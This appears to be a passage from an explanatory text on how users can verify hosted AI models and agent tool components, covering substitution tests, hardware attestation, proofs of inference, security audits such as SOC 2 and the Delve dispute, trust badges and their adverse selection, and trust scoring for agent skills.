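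If a model's weights are secret, the tester has to use the developer's service as the reference. *KBF* (2026), which compares the limits of what models know, detected all 155 substitutions in its test and raised no false alarms in 16 comparisons of a model with itself. *Real Money, Fake Models* (2026) examined unofficial resellers and found that one sold a "GPT-5" and a "GPT-4o-mini" whose answers differed statistically from OpenAI's. It also cautions that passing an equality test doesn't certify a service, since the test covers only the sampled prompts.

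A dishonest provider has several ways to confuse such tests. *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* (2025) mentions compressing the model, substituting another at random, and recognising benchmark questions. Random substitution is effective because it dilutes the evidence. If a provider sends a fraction f of requests to a cheaper model, the distance becomes:

diluted distance = f² × (distance between the two models)

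At f = 0.1 the distance falls to a hundredth, and the tester needs roughly 100 times as many answers to detect it. *Which Model Is Actually Serving You?* (2026) presents a method that estimates this fraction and predicts how many queries an audit will need. A more serious problem is that the provider may recognise the tester, because extra queries don't help if the provider answers all of them with the right model. Testers can reduce this risk by using prompts that look like their normal work.

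Another approach gives a trusted auditor secret information for checking the answers that users see. *Auditor-Assisted Summary-Channel Verification for Hosted LLM Identity Substitution* (2026) proposes doing this with the reasoning summaries that some models display.

None of these tests works well on a remote tool server. The server's answers depend on changing data, and it can do harm without altering those answers, for example by copying the emails it handles.

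### Attested hardware

To learn what a remote machine is running, a user needs evidence from the machine itself. Some processors can provide it by running software in a protected area of memory that the machine's operator isn't supposed to be able to read or change. If Tallyfield, the fictional maker of the database server, offered a remote version on such a processor, the check would work like this:

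1. As the machine starts the protected software, the processor computes a hash of it, called a measurement, and stores the result where that software can't rewrite it.
2. The agent's software sends a fresh random number.
3. The processor signs a report containing the measurement, the random number and a public key that belongs to the protected software.
4. The agent's software checks that the signature comes from a genuine processor with up-to-date security fixes, and that the random number is the one it sent. Otherwise the operator could reuse an old report.
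5. It compares the measurement with the expected hash. If they match, it encrypts the request with the public key, so that only the measured software can read it.

If Tallyfield publishes its source and the build is reproducible, anyone can compute the expected hash independently. If it matches the hash in the report, a review of the source also applies to the running software. Without public source, the report shows only that the server is still running the same undisclosed program.

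For a hosted model, the measurement must also include the weights, and the graphics processor must produce its own report. Even then, the hardware will run a backdoored model just as it would a clean one, and it can't control what happens to data that the measured program sends elsewhere.

The user has to trust the chip maker, its signing keys and the low-level software built into the processor. Researchers have repeatedly broken this protection. In 2024, the BadRAM attack used about $10 of equipment to make memory modules misreport their size, which defeated the protection on AMD server processors. AMD released a fix. In 2025, the Battering RAM and TEE.fail attacks placed small devices between the processor and its memory. TEE.fail extracted signing keys from machines with current Intel processors, which let the researchers forge reports that passed verification.

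Intel and AMD say their products aren't designed to resist physical attacks like these. This matters because the operator of a remote server may own the machine. Attested hardware is more convincing when the operator rents the machine from a large cloud company, because the operator would then need that company's help to attach anything.

Large companies already use the technology for AI. With Apple's Private Cloud Compute, introduced in 2024, an iPhone sends requests only to servers whose software appears in a public log. Meta announced a similar system for WhatsApp's AI features in 2025. Microsoft rents out protected cloud machines with NVIDIA graphics processors. Small publishers of tool servers could use such machines too, but an agent benefits only if its software requests the report and has the expected measurement to check it against.

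### Proofs of execution

Cryptography can replace trust in a chip with a mathematical proof. In a zero-knowledge proof of inference, the provider first publishes a commitment, similar to a hash, to the model's weights. With each answer, it sends a proof that the committed weights produced that answer from the user's request. The user can check the proof without seeing the weights, and a dishonest provider has practically no chance of forging one.

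Producing the proof takes far more computing than producing the answer. zkLLM, a 2024 system by Sun, Li and Zhang, produced a proof smaller than 200 kilobytes but took up to 15 minutes to prove one run of a model with 13 billion parameters. This is much too slow for an agent that calls a model hundreds of times an hour.

Checking a random sample of requests takes much less computation than checking every one. *IMMACULATE* (Guo, Qu and colleagues, 2026) audits a small fraction of requests with verifiable computation, which reduces a service's capacity by less than 1%. The method needs no special hardware and can also detect overcharging. If a provider substitutes another model for 10% of requests, the chance that k random checks all miss it is 0.9^k, which falls below 5% after 29 checks. The audit works only if the provider cooperates and can't predict which requests the auditor will check.

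The same tools can tie an evaluation to particular weights. In an attested evaluation, protected hardware runs the test and signs a report containing hashes of the weights, the test and the scoring program. In 2025, Schnabl and colleagues built a prototype that ran standard benchmarks on a Llama model this way. A zero-knowledge proof could provide the same assurance without trusted hardware, but at 15 minutes per answer, a 1,000-question test would take more than ten days on one machine.

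If the model's provider later attests to the same hash, a user knows that the test result applies to the model answering them. An attested evaluation would have been especially useful for OpenAI's Privacy Filter score, which an outsider could not reproduce exactly. Such an evaluation would not have exposed the SilentCall backdoor unless the test had included a request dated 2026.

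## Audits, certificates and trust scores

A user who can't test a component may rely on somebody else's verdict, such as an auditor's certificate, a badge or a score. The verdict's value as evidence depends on what the assessor examined, who paid for the assessment, and what the assessor stands to lose if it is wrong.

### What SOC 2 and ISO 27001 examine

Software companies commonly display two security credentials, SOC 2 and ISO 27001. SOC 2 is an accounting firm's report on an organisation's controls, the rules and routines it uses to manage risk. According to TechInformed, these controls concern security, availability, processing integrity, confidentiality or privacy. A Type 1 report covers the design of the controls on a given date, while a Type 2 report also covers whether they worked over a period, usually several months. ISO 27001 is an international standard for managing information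 security, and certification requires an independent audit.

Suppose a company requires a second person to approve every change to its software. The auditor picks some changes and looks for the approvals. If 10 of 1,000 changes skipped approval and the auditor checks 25, the chance of missing all 10 is about:

0.99^25 ≈ 0.78

A sample of 25 can show whether the company usually follows its rule, but it can easily miss one bad change. Neither credential identifies a release by its hash. A SOC 2 report covers only the system it describes, which may be a company's hosted service rather than the package it gives away.

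### LiteLLM's certificates and the Delve dispute

When attackers published malicious versions of LiteLLM's Python package in March 2026, the company's website advertised SOC 2 Type 2 and ISO 27001 certification. TechInformed cites a TechCrunch report that Delve, a start-up that sells audit preparation software, had handled the certification work.

Delve was already facing accusations from DeepDelver, an anonymous writer who claimed to work for one of its customers. DeepDelver's *Delve* (2026) alleges that the company gave customers ready-made records of board meetings and tests that never happened, wrote the auditors' conclusions itself, and used audit firms that approved reports without real checks. DeepDelver also says it was possible to publish a page of impressive security measures before doing any of the work. IANS Research's *Delve Allegations Expose Weak Points in Modern Compliance*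 (2026) lists among the allegations that conclusions were written before the period under audit had ended.

Delve denies this. Its *Response to Misleading Claims* states that independent, licensed auditors test the controls and issue the final reports, that customers can choose their own auditor, and that the supposedly fake evidence was templates for customers to edit. Delve's chief executive, Kaushik, later acknowledged in *Delve sets the record straight on anonymous attacks* that the company had grown quickly and fallen short of its own standards. Delve removed some audit firms from its network and offered customers free re-audits. Kaushik also alleged that an attacker had bought Delve's service under false pretences, stolen its data and mixed it with fabricated claims.

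The two sides agree that Delve supplied pre-filled minutes and policies. Delve itself says customers also received a draft report before the auditors tested the controls. An audited company normally describes its own system, so such a draft can be legitimate if the auditors then did their own tests.

Delve argues that similar reports are normal because its customers adopt the same standard controls. This is a fair defence of similar wording, but the AICPA, the American accountants' body behind SOC 2, considers an audit substandard if it isn't designed around the client's own risks and so repeats the risk assessment, sample sizes and tests from the firm's other audits. According to the Journal of Accountancy's *AICPA guides peer reviewers to address SOC 2 risks* (2026), reviewers who suspect this should often compare about five of a firm's audits, because a single file may not reveal it. A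 customer who receives one SOC 2 report usually can't make that comparison.

On 30 March, LiteLLM announced that it would renew both credentials with Vanta, another compliance company, and find independent auditors. Dholakia's *LiteLLM + Vanta* gives no reason beyond a commitment to security. LiteLLM's *Our Updated SOC 2 Type 2 Report Is Available* describes the recertification as complete but doesn't mention ISO 27001. Recertifying was a sensible response to doubts about the old reports, but it is not evidence that they were false.

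### Whether a sound audit would have stopped the attack

A better audit might not have protected LiteLLM's users, even if every accusation against Delve is true. According to Dholakia and Jaff, the attackers stole the publishing token through an unpinned security scanner. SOC 2 covers who can access what, so a thorough auditor might well have objected that the scanner could read the token. If LiteLLM had responded by keeping the token away from the scanner, the attackers could not have stolen it this way.

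A SOC 2 auditor mostly tests the controls a company has chosen, and SOC 2 has no specific rule about pinning build tools. An auditor would normally count a security scan of every build in the company's favour, but in this case the attackers got in through the scanner. A periodic audit would also have been unlikely to catch the attack in time. TechInformed reports that the attackers released malicious versions of the scanner on 19 March, five days before they published the LiteLLM packages.

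A sound audit could have made the attack on LiteLLM less likely, but nobody can say by how much. It could not have been evidence that version 1.82.7 was safe, because the attackers uploaded that version without using LiteLLM's release process. LiteLLM said its hosted service and official Docker image were unaffected, so a certificate for the hosted service could have been accurate while the Python package was stealing passwords.

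### When untrustworthy sites seek the badge

A trust certificate can be worse than having none if the least trustworthy applicants are the most eager to get it, a problem economists call adverse selection. *Adverse Selection in Online "Trust" Certifications* (Edelman, 2009) measured this for TRUSTe and BBBOnLine, two organisations that certified websites' privacy practices.

Edelman compared their membership lists with safety ratings for about half a million popular sites. The ratings came from SiteAdvisor, where Edelman was on the advisory board. SiteAdvisor's software gave each site a unique email address and counted the messages sent to it. The software also installed the sites' programs on separate virtual computers and checked for spyware.

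| Sites | Trustworthy | Untrustworthy | Share untrustworthy |
|---|---|---|---|
| TRUSTe-certified | 874 | 50 | 5.4% |
| Not TRUSTe-certified | 515,309 | 13,148 | 2.5% |
| BBBOnLine-certified | 284 | 3 | 1.0% |
| Not BBBOnLine-certified | 515,898 | 13,196 | 2.5% |

The likelihood ratio for a TRUSTe badge was:

(50 / 13,198) / (874 / 516,183) ≈ 2.2

A visitor who saw the badge should therefore have roughly doubled their estimate of the odds that the site was bad. Sites with downloads or sign-up forms can fail more of SiteAdvisor's tests, but TRUSTe's members still did worse when Edelman compared only such sites. BBBOnLine's ratio was about 0.4, which is reassuring but is based on only three untrustworthy sites.

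Edelman attributes the difference to how the two organisations screened applicants. Both charged fees that could reach $7,000 a year or more, so price alone didn't keep bad sites out. TRUSTe relied mainly on applicants' self-assessments, and had reportedly revoked two certificates in ten years. BBBOnLine evaluated applicants in more detail and required them to belong to a local Better Business Bureau. This process was slow, and BBBOnLine had issued only 631 certificates before it closed the programme to new applicants.

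In its reply to an earlier version of the study, TRUSTe (2006) said that 12% of applicants failed to earn certification and that every certified site had to make changes first. Both statements are consistent with Edelman's figures if untrustworthy sites were more likely to apply. The study shows that the badge was a bad guide to what visitors cared about. It doesn't show that members broke TRUSTe's rules, because those rules didn't restrict some of the behaviour that SiteAdvisor tested for, such as bundling spyware with a download.

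Edelman suggests that such a badge can keep users' trust, and sites can keep paying for it, because many users learn slowly. Later, worse members can then exploit the good name that reputable early members gave it. The share of untrustworthy sites on TRUSTe's full list rose from none of 28 in January 1998 to 3.4% of 1,554 in January 2006. This trend is approximate because Edelman had to judge sites' past conduct by their current behaviour.

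### Paid badges in an AI registry

A registry that sold "verified" badges to tool servers based on a questionnaire would meet all of Edelman's conditions. It would earn money from each badge and lose little when a badge was wrong. Its users would probably be even slower than TRUSTe's to realize that the badges were unreliable, because they may never learn which component harmed them.

A fee could make matters worse. Suppose a registry has 950 honest servers and 50 malicious ones. Most of the honest publishers are volunteers who earn nothing from extra users, so only 10% of them pay. Half of the malicious publishers pay, because one stolen credential would cover the cost. The badge then appears on 95 honest servers and 25 malicious ones:

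malicious share with a badge = 25 / 120 ≈ 21%

malicious share without one = 25 / 880 ≈ 3%

In Spence's model, a signal distinguishes two groups if the weaker group must spend more money or effort to get it. Here, honest and malicious publishers spend the same amount, and the malicious ones gain more.

The identity badges on GitHub and Hugging Face are better than this because the sites check a fact, such as control of a domain, instead of taking the publisher's word. But a user who reads "verified" as "safe" makes the same mistake as visitors who trusted a site because it had a TRUSTe seal. Any registry could repeat Edelman's test on its own records by comparing how often it later removes badged and unbadged components for malware.

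Auditors may soon offer certificates for AI agents themselves. The AICPA is piloting one with the Artificial Intelligence Underwriting Company and expects a full launch in early 2027, according to the Journal of Accountancy. The company being certified will presumably pay for it, as with SOC 2, so the certificate's value as evidence will depend largely on how carefully the assessors test and how often they refuse to certify.

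### Automated ratings and OpenSSF Scorecard

OpenSSF Scorecard is a free tool that can rate any public project, whether or not the project applies. It checks the project's public repository for good security practices, such as code review, recent maintenance, protected branches and pinned dependencies. Each check gives a score from 0 to 10. The overall score is a weighted average, with checks that Scorecard classes as critical counting four times as much as low-risk ones.

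*Do Software Security Practices Yield Fewer Vulnerabilities?* (Zahan, Shohan and colleagues, 2023) tested whether these scores predict the number of reported vulnerabilities in npm and PyPI packages. Its models explained only 9 to 12% of the variation in those numbers. The most informative checks were maintenance, code review, branch protection and security policy. Packages with higher overall scores had more reported vulnerabilities.

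As with the PHP packages, more reports may reflect closer inspection, and well-run projects probably also make reporting easier, so the finding doesn't mean that code review makes software less secure. Still, the study gives reason not to assume that a project scoring 8 out of 10 has fewer flaws than one scoring 5.

Scorecard is more useful as a list of specific weaknesses. One of its checks looks for unpinned dependencies, the mistake that exposed LiteLLM. But the check might have missed that case, because it mainly reads GitHub workflows, container build files and scripts, and LiteLLM ran its scanner on another service, CircleCI.

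### A trust score for agent skills

*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* proposes a score that combines several kinds of evidence about a skill. Each of four signals takes a value from 0 to 1:

- provenance, from an unsigned skill by an anonymous author to a signed, reproducible one from a verified organisation
- behaviour, from critical violations in a code scan to no findings
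- community, based on usage, age, issue reports and reviews
- history, from past security incidents to a clean record

With the default weights, the score is:

trust = 0.3 × provenance + 0.3 × behaviour + 0.2 × community + 0.2 × history

An unsigned skill uploaded yesterday by an anonymous author gets 0 for provenance and community. If the scan finds nothing, the skill gets 1 for behaviour, and it can also get 1 for history because nothing has gone wrong yet. Its score is then 0.3 + 0.2 = 0.5. If the author fakes enough popularity to raise the community signal to 1, the score rises to 0.7, although the skill hasn't changed.

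The paper converts scores into four levels. A score of 0.5 is enough for the third, "community verified", so this skill ranks above "signed" even though it has no signature and no community. The top level starts at 0.75, which an unsigned skill can't reach however popular it seems.

In the example, bought downloads alone might not raise the community signal all the way to 1, because the signal also includes age and reviews. The current software calculates scores from what it can observe locally, such as scan results and declared metadata, so download counts don't yet affect them. This makes the software harder to manipulate than the formula, but according to the paper, it is expected to add such signals as registries mature.

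The paper also multiplies a skill's score by the lowest score among all the skills it depends on, so a skill that scores 0.7 gets 0.42 if its lowest-scoring dependency has 0.6. An attacker can avoid this reduction by publishing a skill with no dependencies.

Finally, the score decays by a factor of e^(−0.01t) over t days without an update, which halves it about every 69 days. This is meant to penalise abandoned skills, but it also penalises finished skills that need no updates. A skill with a score of 0.9 drops to about 0.45 after 70 days, below the anonymous skill uploaded yesterday. An attacker can reset t to zero with a trivial update. The rule also conflicts with the advice to wait before installing new releases.

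The paper proves that more positive evidence never lowers a score and presents this as an incentive for authors to improve their skills, although the guarantee also holds for faked evidence. The experiments confirm that the formula behaves as designed in ten constructed scenarios, but they don't test whether malicious skills get lower scores than benign ones.

### Adding signals up or requiring each one

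A weighted sum lets strength in one area make up for failure in another. A signed, popular skill with a clean history scores 0.7 even if the scan has found a critical violation. The paper suggests that a company might require skills in production to be at least "community verified", and this skill would pass. The paper's installer can separately reject skills that need more access than the company allows, which would block some skills like this one.

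A sum also tells an attacker what to buy. Stealing a signing identity is much harder than buying stars, so if both add points, the attacker will buy the stars. A rule that requires each of several conditions removes this option:

accept only if signed by the expected publisher, and pinned, and free of critical findings

A high star count cannot make up for a missing signature. Requiring every condition also means that honest components fail more often. If honest skills met each of four independent conditions 80% of the time, only about 41% (0.8^4) would meet all four. Each condition therefore needs to address a serious kind of failure. Even then, the malicious TanStack packages would have met the conditions on identity and build records.

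Multiplying likelihood ratios is a better way to combine inconclusive signals than adding weighted scores, provided the signals are independent among malicious components and also among honest ones. A signal that is equally likely in both groups has a ratio of 1, so it doesn't change the result, whereas a weighted sum would still add points for it.

Multiplying correlated signals counts the same evidence more than once. Suppose 1% of skills are malicious, and that stars, downloads and search rank are each high for 40% of honest skills and 20% of malicious ones. Each ratio is 0.5. Treating the three as independent gives:

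0.5 × 0.5 × 0.5 = 0.125

If the three signals were independent, a skill with all three would have about a 0.13% chance of being malicious. If one campaign raises all three together, they count as a single signal with a likelihood ratio of 0.5, and the chance is about 0.5%, four times as high.

The paper calls its four signals "orthogonal", meaning that they measure separate things, but they can still be correlated. A skill with few users is likely to have a clean history because nobody has examined it, so the history signal partly measures how few people use the skill.

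Verdicts from different assessors can also rely on the same evidence. ClawHub's final rating uses the results of its other scanners, so agreement between them isn't fully independent confirmation. Similarly, a SOC 2 report and an ISO 27001 certificate prepared on one platform from the same documents are closer to one piece of evidence than two. When it's unclear how much a group of signals overlaps, the cautious choice is to count only the strongest one.

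### More evidence for more authority

The right amount of evidence also depends on what a component will be able to do. Brandes (2026), in *The Custody Envelope Threshold*, proposes a rule for organisations that ties the two together. An assessor first rates the component's authority in its intended use from 0, for something that never runs, to 3, for something that can affect production systems or credentials. The assessor then rates three safeguards on the same scale:

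- identity, or how exactly the organisation knows which file it is accepting
- ingress, or how well it controls the route by which the file arrives
- revocation, or how well it can withdraw the component if something goes wrong

The organisation should accept the component directly only if:

min(identity, ingress, revocation) ≥ authority

Because the rule takes the minimum, strong identity can't make up for slow revocation. The rule doesn't include popularity, which Brandes argues increases the pressure to accept a component without helping anyone defend the decision afterwards.

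If the bookkeeper's database server held the password to the live accounts, its authority would be 3. A pinned version rates only 2 for identity, so the organisation would also need to verify a signature or build record. It would have to bring the server in through a controlled process, with scanning and approval, and be able to remove it quickly. Alternatively, the organisation could run the server only in a test environment, on a copy of the overdue invoices and without sensitive credentials. That might lower its authority to 1, and much weaker safeguards would be enough.

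This advice is sensible, particularly because an organisation can reduce a component's access even when it can't get better evidence. But the levels are only rankings, so level 2 identity may not be the right match for level 2 authority. Brandes supports the rule by comparing how institutions treat different kinds of components, but doesn't measure whether institutions that follow it have fewer incidents. The safeguards also mostly concern control over a component rather than its quality, so a backdoored model could have a verified publisher, arrive through an approved process and be easy to remove.

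### Legal duties and liability

European law has begun to impose duties on producers whether or not they seek certification. Under the Cyber Resilience Act as adopted, makers of digital products sold in the EU have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities and severe security incidents since 11 September 2026. They must send the authorities an early warning within 24 hours and a fuller notification within 72 hours, and also inform affected users. The secure design requirements take effect later. Volunteers who publish free software outside commercial activity are generally exempt, so many tool servers and skills are not covered.

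A separate directive on product liability applies to products placed on the EU market after 9 December 2026. It treats software, including AI systems, as a product. An injured person has to show that a product was defective and caused the harm, but not that the maker was negligent. The directive covers individuals, not businesses, and excludes the loss of data used for professional purposes, so the bookkeeper's employer could not use it to recover the cost of damaged accounts.

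A badge costs a careful company and a careless one the same fee, whereas a company that accepts liability pays only if its product fails. Suppose each company would owe €1 million for a serious failure, and the yearly chance of one is 1% for the careful company and 10% for the careless one. Their expected yearly costs are €10,000 and €100,000. Accepting liability is therefore more expensive for the worse company, as Spence's condition requires, so a voluntary guarantee is a more credible signal than a purchased badge.

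Edelman suggested making certifiers liable for negligent certificates, but TRUSTe's terms prohibited users from relying on its certifications. Liability would not deter a thief who publishes under a false name, because victims couldn't find the thief to collect damages.
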